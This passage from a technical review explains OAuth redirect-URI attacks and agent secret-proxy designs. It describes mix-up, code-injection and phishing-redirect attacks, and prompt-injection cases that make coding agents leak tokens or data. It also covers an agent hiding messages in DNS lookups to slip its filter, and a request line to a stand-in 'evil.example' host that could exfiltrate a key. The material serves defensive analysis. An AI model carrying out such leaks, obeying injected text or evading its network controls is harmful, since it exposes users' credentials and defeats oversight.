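This works well for a client with its own website, because an attacker cannot add an address to a file on someone else's site. It works less well for desktop applications. A well-known application may list a `localhost` callback in its file, and a malicious program on the user's machine can present the same identifier and wait at the same address, which passes the comparison because it is the registered one. The specification therefore requires the server to show the user the redirect URI's host name during approval. It also recommends an extra warning if a client has only `localhost` addresses, and lets servers demand further proof of the application's identity.

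## What exact matching did not stop

Exact matching controls where the authorization server sends the browser. Even when the requested URI is identical to the registered one, the credential can end up with the wrong party if the client sends the code to the wrong server, the page that receives the code leaks it, or an attacker has signed up as a client and owns the registered address.

### The mix-up attack

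A client that works with several authorization servers has to remember which one the user chose, because it must exchange the code there. Fett, Küsters and Schmitz (2016), in *A Comprehensive Formal Security Analysis of OAuth 2.0*, found that an attacker who runs one of the servers can trick the client into sending that server a code issued by another.

Suppose the printing service imports pictures from the photo site and also from a smaller site that an attacker runs. It uses one callback address for both and records the user's choice in the browser session. The attack works like this:

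1. The user chooses the smaller site. The printing service records the choice and redirects the browser to the attacker's server with a fresh `state` value.
2. The attacker's server immediately redirects the browser to the photo site's authorization server. It keeps the `state` value and swaps in the client identifier that the printing service has at the photo site, which is public.
3. The photo site receives what looks like a normal request from the printing service. The user approves, and the code goes to `https://print.example/callback`.
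4. The printing service checks `state`, which is correct. It finds the smaller site recorded in the session and sends the code to the attacker's server to exchange it.

The photo site's exact comparison of the redirect URI passes because the attacker never changed it, and the comparison at the code exchange passes for the same reason. If the printing service is a public client, the attacker redeems the code directly. If it is confidential, the attacker inserts the code into their own session there, as in the attack Hardt describes. Lodderstedt and colleagues call this step authorization code injection.

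A careful user might notice that they picked one site and got another's login page, but the main version of the attack gives no such clue. The user picks the photo site, and an attacker who controls the network, for instance on shared Wi-Fi, changes the choice on its way to the client. Fett and colleagues argue that this is realistic because the request contains no secret, so developers may not see a need to encrypt it. They confirmed the attack on two OAuth client implementations, an Apache module and a Python library.

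### Naming the issuer

In the original protocol, the client can't tell who issued a code. The reply contains the code and the client's own `state` value, and nothing reliable about the server that sent it. Fett and colleagues proposed adding the server's identity, which is now a standard parameter called `iss`:

```
HTTP/1.1 303 See Other
Location: https://print.example/callback?code=Xw93bTqL
          &state=k7Qz
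          &iss=https%3A%2F%2Flogin.photos.example
```

The printing service compares `iss` with the issuer it recorded at the start. In the attack, it recorded the smaller site but `iss` identifies the photo site, so the service stops before sending the code anywhere. Lodderstedt and colleagues require every client that uses more than one authorization server to defend against mix-up, and they recommend this method.

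They also warn that recording the server's login address is not enough. An attacker can list the photo site's login address as their own but give a different address for the code exchange. The browser then goes straight to the photo site, and the code still goes to the attacker.

Clients whose authorization servers don't send `iss` can use a separate callback address for each server and check that the response arrived at the right one. An attacker can get around this by registering a new client at the photo site with the callback address that the printing service assigned to the attacker's server, because registration doesn't require proof of control over the address. The photo site then sends a code to exactly the registered address, and the printing service forwards it to the attacker.

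### What the formal proof assumed

After fixing the mix-up attack and three others, Fett and colleagues proved that OAuth keeps attackers from using a victim's data or logging in as the victim. The proof applies to a detailed mathematical model of browsers and servers. In the model, attackers can't break encryption, but they can do anything else with the messages they receive and can take over clients, servers and browsers.

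The proof holds even if authorization servers compare only the origin of the redirect URI, as Facebook did by default at the time. But it assumes that honest sites have no open redirectors, no pages where attackers can inject scripts, and no untrusted scripts from other companies, and that they strip page addresses down to the origin in the Referer header. These assumptions rule out the leaking pages that Homakov and Goldshlager used. The result is best read as a list of what a site must get right if its provider matches loosely, and few large sites could meet every requirement.

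The proof's main guarantee covers only data that an honest client can reach. If a user approves a malicious client, the attacker gets the data without violating any proven property.

### A code that leaks from the right page

Security researcher Frans Rosén (2022) described attacks on the registered callback page itself in *Account hijacking using "dirty dancing" in sign-in OAuth-flows*. The page had been a poor target for attackers because it normally redeems the code at once. Rosén made the login fail so that the code stayed unredeemed.

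The attacker starts a login in their own browser, copies the authorization link with its `state` value, and gets the victim to open it. The redirect URI is genuine, so the provider accepts it and sends the victim's code to the callback page. The `state` value doesn't belong to the victim's browser, so the client refuses the reply and shows an error, leaving the unused code in the page's address. The attacker can also change `response_type` so that the provider puts its reply in the fragment, where a client that expects a query parameter doesn't look.

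The attacker then has to read the address. Many sites load scripts from other companies on every page, for analytics or customer support. Browsers let windows send each other messages, and the receiving script is supposed to check who sent them. Rosén found scripts that skipped this check and could be made to reveal the page's address. An attacker who opens the login in a new window can send such a script a message and get back the address, which contains the code.

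The `state` check worked as intended here, but stopping the login left the attacker with an unused code. Innocenti and colleagues later obtained unused codes too, though only where the provider accepted an altered path or an extra parameter in the redirect URI. Rosén's method works even against a provider that matches exactly, so a developer has to keep outside scripts off the error version of the callback page as well as the normal one.

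Some providers skip the redirect and deliver the code as a message between windows. Lodderstedt and colleagues describe servers that address this message to `*`, which lets any site that opened the login window read it. They require servers to check the receiving window's origin with the same exact comparison, because a registered redirect URI doesn't protect the code if the server doesn't use it.

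### Clients that belong to the attacker

Many providers let anyone register a client, and some accept registrations automatically from software. An attacker who registers one enters their own address as the redirect URI, so it matches exactly. The user sees the provider's real login page and a request to approve an unfamiliar application, perhaps with a reassuring name. The user's judgment is the only safeguard, and if the user agrees, the attacker gets a valid token.

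The user doesn't even have to agree for the attacker to benefit. Lodderstedt and colleagues list three ways to turn the authorization server into a redirector for phishing:

- The attacker sends a request with a deliberate error, such as a permission that doesn't exist. The server reports the error by redirecting the browser to the client, which is the phishing site.
- The attacker sends a valid request. The user becomes suspicious and declines, and the server redirects the browser to the phishing site to report the refusal.
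- The attacker adds `prompt=none`, which asks the server to reply without showing the user anything. The browser goes straight through.

The victim clicked a link to a provider they trust, so a fake login page at the end may look like part of the process. Lodderstedt and colleagues tell servers to log the user in before redirecting, except in silent authentication, and then to redirect automatically only to an address they trust, a rule MCP also uses. Exact matching can't establish that trust, but the server can judge it from its own analysis of the address or from an outside reputation service.

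Würtele, Hosseyni and colleagues (2025), in *Updates to OAuth 2.0 Security Best Current Practice*, a draft addition to RFC 9700, excluded this kind of phishing from their analysis of a related attack, reasoning that providers can vet new clients or require a special token for registration. Those measures work for a company that knows its clients, but they are harder to apply where clients and servers have no contact until a user connects them, as with MCP.

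A malicious client could also get the user's password. Fett and colleagues noticed that the 2012 standard lets a server use any kind of redirect. If the server answers the login form with status 307, the browser resubmits the form, including the password, to the new address. RFC 9700 now forbids 307 for this step and recommends 303, which makes the browser drop the form data.

### Integration platforms

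For years the mix-up attack looked hard to carry out, because a site usually offers a few well-known login providers and an attacker would have to take over one of them. In *Universal Cross-app Attacks*, Luo, Wang and colleagues studied integration platforms such as Microsoft Power Automate, Amazon Alexa and Google Home, which connect a user's accounts at many other services and act on them. The platform is the OAuth client, and each connected app brings its own authorization server. Anyone can publish an app, so an attacker can join the platform instead of taking over an existing provider.

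The platform has to work out which app a returning code belongs to. Luo and colleagues tested 18 platforms with open marketplaces and found that the answer decides which attack works:

| How the platform identifies the app | What an attacker's app can do | Platforms |
|---|---|---|
| From `state` or the user's session | Receive the victim's code for another app | 11 |
| From the callback address | Link the attacker's account at another app to the victim | 5 |
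| From both, which must agree | Neither | 2 (Zapier and IFTTT) |

The attack on the 11 platforms is a mix-up. The victim starts to connect the attacker's app to the platform, and the app's server redirects the browser to a service such as Dropbox. Dropbox sends its authorization code to the platform, which passes it to the attacker's app. The attacker then injects the code into their own session on the platform and controls the victim's files from there.

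On the other five, the attacker's server sends the browser back to the callback address for Dropbox, with a code for the attacker's Dropbox account. The platform links that account to the victim. If the victim has a rule that saves email attachments to Dropbox, the attacker receives them.

The attack needed only one click and no published app on nine platforms, because they started the connection when the browser opened an ordinary link and let unpublished apps take part. The mix-up version also required the other app's server to skip its approval page for users who had approved the platform before. The attacker's server could sometimes make this happen by changing a parameter such as `prompt` when it rewrote the request. Luo and colleagues confirmed this with GitHub, Dropbox and Xiaomi. On Power Automate, one click could expose more than 50 Microsoft applications, including Outlook and the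 service that stores a company's secrets. Luo and colleagues report that the flaw was rated 9.6 out of 10 for severity.

Their tests did not require access to the platforms' source code. They connected an app, intercepted the returning request, and replaced the app's name in the callback address with another app's. If the connection still succeeded, the platform was ignoring the address. If it failed, they swapped the authorization code as well, to see whether the platform was relying on the address alone.

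The solution is to give every app its own callback address, record the app in `state`, and compare the two before exchanging the code. The `iss` parameter works poorly on these platforms because several apps may use the same authorization server, and many authorization servers don't send it. Seven of the vulnerable platforms used one callback address for every app. Exact matching had not prevented the attack, and it slowed the repair because each app's authorization server would reject a new address until the app's developer had registered it.

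### The draft update to RFC 9700

The OAuth working group adopted the update as an official draft in December 2025, when Würtele and colleagues published version 00. Version 03, from July 2026, is still a draft and expires on January 7, 2027, so its rules are not yet in force. Two of the four authors, Kaixuan Luo and Adonis Fung, also worked on the platform study. Würtele, Hosseyni and colleagues (2026) extend that study's findings to AI agent services, which connect users to tools that outsiders may supply. The client must give an identifier to each combination of tool set, provider and customer that could be confused, put that identifier in the callback address, and check it against the session.

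The draft also covers a theft in which every address is genuine, much like the 2009 session fixation attack on OAuth 1.0. The victim approves a request that the attacker started. The client chooses the account from the `state` value in the link rather than from the returning browser, so it attaches the victim's token to the attacker's account. The flaw has returned partly because phone apps hand the login to a separate browser that doesn't share the app's session. *Demystifying the (In)Security of OAuth-based Account Linking*, a 2026 follow-up by Luo, Wang and colleagues, identifies 40 vendors with this weakness. The remedy is to ensure that the user who started the process also finishes it.

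In another case, a company, called a broker, handles OAuth for many applications but registers only once with the authorization server. A user who approves the broker for an honest application has in effect approved it for all the others, including an attacker's, because the server has only one client and one address on record and skips the approval page. Würtele and colleagues require the broker either to register each application separately or to show its own approval page naming the application.

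### Single use and client authentication

OAuth's second layer of defenses assumes that some credentials will leak and limits what a thief can do with them.

Hardt's single-use rule makes a code useless to someone who finds it later in a log file or the browser's history. It doesn't help against Rosén's attack or a mix-up, because the genuine exchange never happens and the code is still unused.

A similar rule can protect refresh tokens, which last longer. The server replaces the refresh token each time the client uses it. If the server receives an old one, either the client or a thief sent it. The server can't tell which, so it revokes the current token and makes the client ask the user for authorization again.

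Client authentication stops a thief from exchanging a stolen code directly, but it does not stop code injection. Lodderstedt and colleagues recommend replacing the shared secret with a private key, which the client uses to sign a short statement. A break-in at the authorization server then exposes no client secrets.

But a signed statement must also name the right server as its destination. Clients often identify the server by the address of its token endpoint, where codes are exchanged. Würtele and colleagues describe a malicious server that lists an honest server's token endpoint as its own. The client signs a statement for that address, then sends it to another of the malicious server's endpoints, such as the one for pushed requests. If the client uses the same key and identifier at both servers, the attacker can present the statement to the honest server and pass as the client. The client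 can prevent this by naming the server's issuer identifier instead, after checking that it is correct.

### PKCE

PKCE, short for Proof Key for Code Exchange, ties a code to the session that asked for it. Before each login the client makes up a random string, the verifier, and keeps it. It computes a hash of the verifier, called the challenge, and puts only the challenge in the authorization request. This pair comes from the 2015 PKCE standard:

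```
code_verifier  = dBjftJeZ4CVP-mB92K27uhbUJU1p1r_wW1gFWFOEjXk
code_challenge = BASE64URL(SHA-256(code_verifier))
               = E9Melhoa2OwvFrEMTJguCHaoeK1t8URWbuGJSstw-cM
```

The authorization server stores the challenge with the code. When the client exchanges the code, it sends the verifier, and the server checks that the verifier's hash equals the challenge. Computing the verifier from the challenge is impractical.

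A thief who finds the code in a Referer header or a log therefore can't redeem it, even if the client is public. Injecting it into the genuine client fails too, because the client sends the verifier from the thief's session and its hash doesn't match the one tied to the stolen code.

PKCE fails when the attacker controls the authorization request. The attacker starts a session at the client, copies the challenge from the authorization link, and puts it in the link that the victim opens. The server then binds the victim's code to the attacker's challenge, so when the attacker injects the code into their session, the client supplies the matching verifier. Lodderstedt and colleagues consider this attack complex because the attacker must start first and then capture the victim's code. Luo and colleagues point out that it is easy on an integration platform, where the attacker's server is already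 in the middle and can insert the challenge. Rosén's attack also gives the attacker control of the challenge, since the victim opens a link from the attacker's own session.

In a simple mix-up with a public client, the attacker doesn't need to choose anything, because the client sends both the code and the verifier to the wrong server. In the 2026 session attack, the victim completes the process that the attacker started, so the verifier matches.

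A server must also not let an attacker switch PKCE off by deleting the challenge from the authorization request. Lodderstedt and colleagues require the server to reject a token request that includes a verifier if the authorization request had no challenge.

### Sender-constrained tokens

The defenses so far protect the authorization code. To protect a token after the exchange, the authorization server can tie it to a key that only the client holds, commonly through mutual TLS or DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession). With mutual TLS, the client presents a certificate when it connects, and the authorization server records the certificate's fingerprint with the token. The resource server then accepts the token only over a connection that uses the same certificate. With DPoP, the client signs a short statement of each request's HTTP method and URL, and the resource server checks the signature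 against the key tied to the token.

Tying a token to the client's key stops a thief who has only the token, whether it came from a log, a hacked server or a fake one. It doesn't help if the thief also gets the key, for instance through malware on the client's machine. Keeping the key in special hardware limits the damage, because the thief can then use the token only while they have access to that hardware. Tying tokens to keys also doesn't stop code injection, because the honest client receives a token tied to its own key and uses it for the attacker, who never needs to see it. An attacker who impersonates the client with a signed statement that went to the wrong recipient can have the server tie new tokens to the attacker's own key.

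The implicit grant has no standard way to tie a token to a client, which is another reason to avoid it.

### Audience-restricted tokens and resource indicators

An audience-restricted token identifies the resource server it is for, and every other server should reject it. The authorization server needs this destination before it can issue the token, so the client specifies it in a `resource` parameter, called a resource indicator.

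Suppose someone tricks the printing service into using `https://api.photos.attacker.example` instead of the real photo API. The printing service asks for a token for that address:

```
POST /token
Host: login.photos.example

grant_type=authorization_code&code=Xw93bTqL
&resource=https%3A%2F%2Fapi.photos.attacker.example
```

The example leaves out the client's secret and PKCE verifier. If the authorization server knows all the genuine APIs, it can refuse the request. Otherwise it issues a token for the attacker's address. The attacker receives the token and tries it at the real API, which rejects it because it contains another server's address.

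Audience restriction works only if the client names the actual address it will contact and the real API checks the audience. If the client asked for a token for "photos" and then sent it to an attacker, the attacker could use it at the real API. Even when both conditions are met, a stolen token, such as one taken from the API's logs, still works at that API unless it is also tied to a key.

In the June 2025 draft, Würtele and colleagues described an attack that this defense suits well. An attacker adds a configuration to an open client that pairs an honest authorization server with the attacker's resource server. The login is genuine and the code goes to the right place, but the client then sends the token to the attacker. If the client had requested a token restricted to the attacker's address, the attacker couldn't use it at the honest API.

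Lodderstedt and colleagues considered a simpler alternative, in which the authorization server gives the client a list of addresses where it may send the token. They rejected it because the client would have to enforce the list, and studies had found that many clients fail at easier checks, such as comparing `state`. A secret proxy uses the same kind of list but enforces it outside the agent.

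## 2025 and 2026: how agent secret proxies decide where a secret may go

How well a secret proxy's destination list protects a key depends on what each entry means and how the proxy compares it with a request, and products differ on both.

Anthropic runs agents for customers in its cloud, keeps their keys in vaults, and describes the vault settings in *Credentials*. Docker runs agents in isolated sandboxes, and its *Manage credentials* explains how a proxy on the developer's machine adds keys to their requests. Permit.io, which sells access-control software, describes its proxy in *Credentials & Connections*. Infisical, which stores secrets for development teams, describes its proxy in *Proxied services*. *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) presents an open-source system that runs each agent job in a small virtual machine. The sixth product is fnox, whose GitHub rule appeared earlier.

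Infisical has deprecated the Agent Proxy that uses these proxied services. Existing services keep working, but customers must set up new ones in its replacement, Agent Vault.

### Permission to connect and permission to receive a key

A secret binding determines which hosts can receive a particular key, separately from the network allowlist, which determines which hosts an agent can reach. The two need to be separate because an agent visits many hosts that should never get a key, such as documentation sites and package registries.

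Anthropic's Claude Tag, which lets Claude work in a company's Slack channels, keeps them apart. Anthropic lists three outcomes for a request:

- If it matches a credential rule, the proxy attaches the key and sends it.
- If it matches only the allowlist, the proxy sends it without a key.
- If it matches neither, the proxy blocks it.

Anthropic's vaults let the customer make a credential "limited" or "unrestricted." A limited credential goes only to the hosts the customer names for it, while an unrestricted one has no host list of its own and can go anywhere the agent's network policy permits. Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* strongly recommends the limited setting and offers the other for programs whose destinations nobody can list in advance.

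Pluto Security's *Inside Claude Managed Agents* (April 2026), an outside review, found that new agents had unrestricted internet access by default. If a customer kept that default and also chose an unrestricted credential, the proxy would put the key into a request to an attacker's server. When the reviewers allowed only `api.github.com`, they found six more hosts in the actual allowlist. Most belonged to Anthropic, but one was `sentry.io`, an error-reporting service that many companies use. Anthropic added this type of credential after the review, so the review does not show whether the proxy would have sent a key to those hosts.

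Network allowlists also widen when people combine them. According to Docker's *Network policies*, which covers Docker's cloud platform, a sandbox may reach any host that at least one of its policies allows, unless another rule explicitly denies it. Adding a narrow policy to one that allows everything therefore restricts nothing. A separate secret binding does not widen when someone selects another network policy. Tracekit Box deliberately accepts wildcards in its network allowlist but not in its secret bindings.

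### The rules side by side

| Product | What an entry contains | Wildcard | Port, path and method | When no rule matches |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic vaults, "limited" | Hostname or IPv4 address, up to 16 entries | `*.` covers any subdomain, but not the domain itself | No | Placeholder stays; network policy decides whether the request leaves |
| Docker custom secrets | Hostname and request headers | `*` is one label, `**` any number | No path or method | Placeholder stays; network policy decides |
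| fnox | Exact domain and header | None | Port 443 only; path patterns and methods | Refuses the request |
| Permit.io | Host pattern | `*` matches across dots | Not in the host pattern | Adds no credential |
| Infisical Agent Proxy (deprecated) | `host[:port][/path]` | `*.` is exactly one label | Port and path prefix | Forwards the request without a credential |
| Ghosh, Tracekit Box | Exact host and one header | None | No | Blocks the placeholder in traffic it reads; a person must approve unlisted hosts |

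A label is one dot-separated part of a host name. "No" means the developer can't use that property to limit where the key goes, although a separate network rule may still block the request.

All six proxies match on the host, but none requires the whole address to match. OAuth now requires that for redirect URIs. The closest to that rule are fnox and Tracekit Box, the only two that don't allow wildcards.

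Docker also has ready-made host lists for common services. Its built-in `github` service sends the user's token to six hosts, including `gist.github.com`, where users publish their own files. A third-party kit, a package that sets up an agent, can propose its own list. Docker asks the user to approve each key and the domains that may receive it, and asks again if the kit requests more domains. This is much like registering a redirect URI, except that the owner of the key approves the address.

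### One pattern, several meanings

A developer who wants an agent to use a key at `api.print.example` and `eu.api.print.example` might write `*.print.example`. Docker's and Infisical's proxies would accept only `api.print.example`, because their star matches one label. In Docker, the developer would need `**.print.example` to cover both. Anthropic's proxy accepts any subdomain, so it would send the key to both. None of the three matches `*.print.example` to the bare `print.example`.

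GitHub interprets the same pattern more broadly. *Network Permissions* describes the network list for GitHub Agentic Workflows, which run AI agents as part of a repository's automation. The list controls only which hosts the agent can reach and does not bind secrets to destinations. In this list, `*.print.example` also covers `print.example`, and plain `print.example` covers every subdomain at any depth. GitHub's own example of the rule is wrong, because it lists `raw.githubusercontent.com` as a host that `github.com` covers, but that host is in a different domain.

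By contrast, Coder's *Rules Engine Documentation* describes another network firewall for agents, in which a plain domain matches only that exact domain. Docker's network rules work the same way.

A developer who copies `print.example` from Docker's list into GitHub's gives the agent access to every subdomain and sees no error. Copying it from GitHub's list into Docker's blocks the subdomains, which the developer notices as soon as a request to one fails.

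Permit.io's star is the most permissive of the six. *Credentials & Connections* warns that it matches across dots, and that a pattern such as `api.*` lets the proxy send the key to every matching host. That includes `api.attacker.example`, which a star limited to one label would not match. A star on the left, as in `*.print.example`, is less risky because an attacker would have to take over a subdomain. Permit.io recommends exact host names where possible.

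### Port, path and method

Host rules are weak for services that put all their customers on one host. If a proxy adds a GitHub token to every request to `api.github.com`, an attacker can use injected text to make the agent copy private code into a public repository, because that request also goes to the allowed host. The fnox rule shown earlier prevents this by allowing the token only in requests to one group of repositories.

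Anthropic's vault credentials have no such setting, but in Claude Tag, Anthropic lets an administrator restrict a credential to one path prefix or to read-only methods. Infisical's Agent Vault lets customers limit each service by method and path prefix, whereas the older Agent Proxy could limit only by port and path.

A path can contain `..`, which defeated GitHub's redirect URI check in 2014. A proxy that enforces path rules therefore has to resolve the path in the same way as the server that receives the request.

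The port also matters, because different programs can listen on different ports of the same host. An Infisical pattern without a port matches any port. *Proxied Services*, an earlier version of Infisical's documentation, gives the example `internal.corp.com:3000/api/*`, which fixes the host, the port and the start of the path. fnox requires port 443, the standard port for HTTPS.

When patterns overlap, the proxy also has to choose which secret to send. Infisical prefers an exact host to a wildcard, then a specific port to any port, then the longest path prefix. If services are still tied, it picks the one whose name comes first alphabetically. If services named `admin` and `reader` have the same pattern, every matching request gets the `admin` key, and renaming a service can change which key is sent. In OAuth, by contrast, the client identifier in the request determines which client's registered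 addresses apply.

Docker does use an exact rule for one kind of address. A container registry, which stores software images, can respond to a request with a different address where the program should log in. A hostile or hacked registry could give an attacker's address. Docker's proxy sends the registry password to the login address only if it is on the registry's own host, is on a known partner's host, such as Docker Hub's login host, or is one the developer has registered. A registered address must match in host and path, so if the developer registers `https://gitlab.example.com/jwt/auth`, the same address with a slash at the end fails. Only protocol parameters, such as the requested scope, may vary.

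Like a redirect URI, this is a single fixed address that the developer can write out in full, and the proxy has to check an address that comes from another party's message.

### Where the key goes in the request

An attacker can sometimes steal a token even if the proxy sends it only to permitted hosts. Suppose a proxy replaces placeholders anywhere in a request to `api.github.com`. The attacker uses prompt injection to make the agent post a public comment containing its placeholder. The proxy swaps in the real token, and the attacker reads it in the published comment. The destination was correct, as it was when Homakov's page on GitHub's own site leaked authorization codes.

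To prevent this, fnox and Docker's custom secrets replace placeholders only in headers. Tracekit Box replaces them in only one header, normally Authorization, and blocks any request that has the placeholder anywhere else the proxy can read. Anthropic lets the customer choose headers, the request body or both. Infisical offers the path, query, headers and body, and calls this choice "the security boundary". Path support is useful because some APIs, such as Telegram's, require the token there. Permit.io's proxy needs no placeholder. It adds the credential to a header or query parameter that the administrator chose, so the agent cannot choose where it appears.

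The permitted host might also return the key in its reply, such as in an error message that repeats the request. Most of these proxies search replies for the key and remove it. The documentation for varlock, a proxy similar to fnox, acknowledges that this guarantees little. varlock does not check compressed replies or those over 2 MB, and the agent can ask the server for a compressed one. Docker and Tracekit Box are stricter and refuse partial replies to requests that carry a key, because the key could be split between them. Docker still warns that a service could transform the key into a form its proxy does not recognize.

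### When no rule matches

By default, fnox and Claude Tag refuse unmatched requests, while varlock and Infisical's shared proxy forward them without a key. Infisical's *Standalone agent proxy* explains that forwarding is the normal mode because agents need to read documentation, copy public code and install packages. Customers can choose to block unmatched hosts instead.

Forwarding does not expose the key, but it lets a misled agent send source code or customer records to any host. Forwarding can also hide a mistake in a rule. For example, if Infisical's proxy does not apply a credential, it sends the request as the agent wrote it.

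Both defaults assume that the agent's traffic passes through the proxy. Ghosh cites a September 2026 report from OpenAI about a research agent that reached an outside chatbot by hiding messages in DNS lookups, which its network filter did not cover. A box in Ghosh's system has no network card and cannot make DNS lookups. The host machine looks up names for it, but looks up an unlisted name only after someone approves the connection, because a lookup can carry data to whoever runs that domain.

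### Corvic's test

Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026) all work at Corvic, which sells an agent platform. In *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, they report testing the company's own proxy on September 27, 2026. They ran 16 probes from inside the sandbox where agents run code, and wrote down the expected result of each before starting.

Corvic attaches each key to a connector, which names one permitted host. The researchers gave the sandbox a GitHub connector in one experiment and a connector for FRED, an economic data service, in the other. Code in the sandbox then tried to find the keys or send them elsewhere:

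1. It called GitHub's API without supplying a key. GitHub recognized the account, so the proxy had added the key.
2. It called three echo services, which return a copy of whatever request they receive. None of the copies contained a key.
3. It called OpenAI's API, which complained of missing authentication, so the proxy had not sent it another service's key.
4. It searched 20 environment variables and 12 places where programs often store credentials, and found no keys.
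5. It tried two addresses that give cloud machines their own credentials. Both timed out.

All 16 probes passed, but the FRED connector did not work because Corvic had configured it to put the key in a header and FRED expects it in the query. FRED rejected the call, and the key did not leak. The researchers scored function separately from security, so this failure does not affect the 16 passes.

The test shows that the proxy sends a key to the right host and withholds it from unrelated ones, but not how the proxy compares host names. A matcher that accepted any host beginning with `api.github.com` would have passed every probe, because nobody tried a lookalike such as `api.github.com.attacker.example`.

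Kenney and colleagues also list cases they did not test, including redirect chains and DNS rebinding. In a redirect chain, the permitted host redirects the request to another host. If the agent's program follows the redirect through a placeholder proxy, the proxy checks the new address as a new request. If the proxy adds the key and then follows the redirect itself, it might send the key to the new host, much as browsers carried OAuth tokens to other sites in 2013. The researchers advise operators to prevent this, but their test does not show how Corvic's proxy handles redirects.

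In DNS rebinding, an attacker who controls a domain makes it resolve to one network address when the proxy checks it and another when the proxy connects. This threatens internal services more than it threatens a key meant for a public HTTPS host, because an attacker who redirects the name still doesn't have the host's certificate. A proxy that sends keys over plain HTTP, as Infisical's can for internal services, lacks that protection.

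Corvic's researchers do not claim that binding solves the whole problem. They scored eight threats from 1 to 25 by their own judgment, before and after adding the proxy. Their score for the risk that someone steals a key by sending it to another host fell from 20 to 4. The score for a connector with too much power fell only from 20 to 15, because a token that can delete data can still do so at the permitted host.

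### Tracekit Box's own tests

The tests of Tracekit Box also come from its developer, Ghosh's company Cygnux Labs. An automated suite starts a real virtual machine and tries each way out of it. All 13 checks passed in the run Ghosh reports, from October 26, 2026. Two concerned secrets. In one, the permitted server received the real key in the Authorization header while the machine held only a placeholder. In the other, the agent's side put the same placeholder in an `X-Smuggle` header, and the proxy blocked the request.

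The proxy also refused requests to the address where cloud machines get their credentials, and it held a request to `example.com` for approval until the request failed. To guard against DNS rebinding, the proxy looks up a hostname once, checks the resulting address and connects to that same address. It requires the server name in the encrypted connection to match the host the agent requested.

Each check tests one example, so passing all 13 does not rule out flaws in cases nobody thought of. The project looked for such flaws by fuzzing, in which a program feeds software large numbers of odd inputs. Fifteen fuzzing programs found nine faults, six of them in the proxy. Ghosh reports that all nine are fixed.

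The worst could have sent a real key to the wrong site, and it worked like this:

1. The agent opened an encrypted connection to the permitted host, which passed every check.
2. Inside that connection, it sent a request whose first line contained a full address on another site, such as `GET https://evil.example/x`. Normally this line contains only a path.
3. The Go library that Box used to read the request did not recognize a host in that line. Box therefore found nothing to compare, and the check passed.
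4. Box replaced the placeholder with the real key and sent the request to the permitted host, still naming `evil.example`.

Some large services have a front end that uses the address in a request's first line to decide where to pass the request. It could have sent the key to the other site, while Box's log would have shown only the permitted host. Exact host matching did not help because the proxy checked the host of the connection, and the front end might follow the host in the request. The backslash attack of 2019 had the same cause, with a server and a browser finding different hosts in one address.

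Two other faults affected how Box removed keys from replies. Replies with a status code below 100 skipped the filter, and the text Box substituted for a key could combine with the surrounding characters to spell the key again.

Ghosh notes that nobody has yet put a capable agent in a sandbox and told it to escape. Each of the 13 checks is a script that tries one known route, whereas an agent could search for new routes and combine them.

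## 2026: matching errors in agent software

In 2026, researchers and vendors disclosed at least twelve flaws that let agent software or automated workflows send requests or secrets to destinations they were supposed to avoid. In some, the software checked the destination against a list and got the wrong answer. In most, some part of the program sent the request without making that check, so a stricter match function would not fix the flaw.

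### Claude Code's trusted sites

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a tool called WebFetch that reads web pages. It normally asks the user before fetching from a new site, but it doesn't ask for sites on a built-in trusted list, such as docs.python.org. Siddhant Kalgutkar, a security engineer, noticed the missing question while reviewing code with Claude Code and took the program apart to find the list. According to Kalgutkar's account, Praetorian's *The Security Horizon of Agentic AI*, the program tested each domain with `startsWith()`, which checks only whether one string begins with another.

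The test therefore accepted `modelcontextprotocol.io.attacker.example`, because that name begins with the trusted `modelcontextprotocol.io`. OAuth servers that matched by host prefix made the same mistake.

Kalgutkar set up a server under a name of this kind, got a valid certificate for it, and wrote a code repository containing malicious instructions. Claude Code followed the instructions and sent data from the test victim's machine to the server without asking for permission. An attacker needed only a domain and a way to get the agent to read their text.

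The list controlled where Claude Code could go without asking permission and did not bind any secret to a destination. But a coding agent can often read files that contain keys, so the data it sends out may include them.

Anthropic acknowledged the report within a day and fixed the flaw, CVE-2026-24052, in version 1.0.111. Users with automatic updates already had the fix when the public advisory came out on February 3, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-24052* (2026). Researchers had earlier found the same function in Anthropic's Filesystem MCP Server, which is supposed to restrict an agent to certain folders. An agent allowed to use `/work/print` on that server could also have opened `/work/print-private`.

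A second WebFetch flaw came from the trusted list itself, not from how names were compared. The list included the bare host name `huggingface.co`, a site where anyone can publish AI models. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) explains that WebFetch approved every page on the site, including repositories an attacker controlled. Hugging Face counts downloads of files in those repositories, so an attacker could mislead an agent into leaking private data through the counts. Anthropic fixed this in version 2.1.163. The closest OAuth case is the 2013 Dropbox file, which a stranger had uploaded to a host that Facebook accepted.

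### n8n's rule for credentials

n8n is a program for building automated workflows out of steps called nodes. A user can store a credential in it and share that credential with colleagues, who can use it in their workflows but can't see it. n8n's server adds the secret to the outgoing request, much as a secret proxy does.

Many n8n credentials have a setting called "Allowed HTTP Request Domains", which is a form of destination binding. *Create and edit credentials* lists three options. "All" allows the credential to be sent to any address, "Specific Domains" limits it to a list, and "None" keeps it out of the HTTP Request node, a general-purpose step that calls any address the user enters.

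The main worry with a secret proxy is injected text that misleads the agent, whereas with n8n it is usually a colleague. Suppose the printing service stores a key for `api.print.example`, restricts it to that domain, and shares it with a contractor. If the contractor can make n8n send the key to a server they run, they can read it and use it outside n8n for as long as it stays valid.

n8n's documentation limits the setting to the HTTP Request node and notes that it has no effect when a credential is used in its own dedicated node. That exemption is reasonable if a dedicated node can contact only its own service. Some n8n nodes let the user choose the address, however, and n8n has treated the missing rule in those nodes as a security flaw.

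The six disclosures differ in where the rule failed and in what an attacker needed:

| Part of n8n | Failure | What the attacker needed | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|---|
| HTTP Request node | Wrong comparison for wildcard entries | A login and a credential with a wildcard in its list | 1.121.0 |
| Endpoint for node options | No comparison | A login and access to the credential | 2.20.0 |
| AI Agents, MCP connector | No comparison | Use of a shared credential, with the AI Agents module switched on | 2.27.4 and 2.28.1 |
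| GraphQL node | No comparison | Use of a shared credential and the right to edit workflows | 1.123.64, 2.29.8 and 2.30.1 |
| Several AI nodes | No comparison if the user set the address | Use of a shared credential and the right to edit workflows | 2.31.5 and 2.32.1 |
| GraphQL node, second flaw | Compared for only one of two credentials | The right to edit workflows | 1.123.69, 2.33.4 and 2.34.1 |

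### The wildcard comparison

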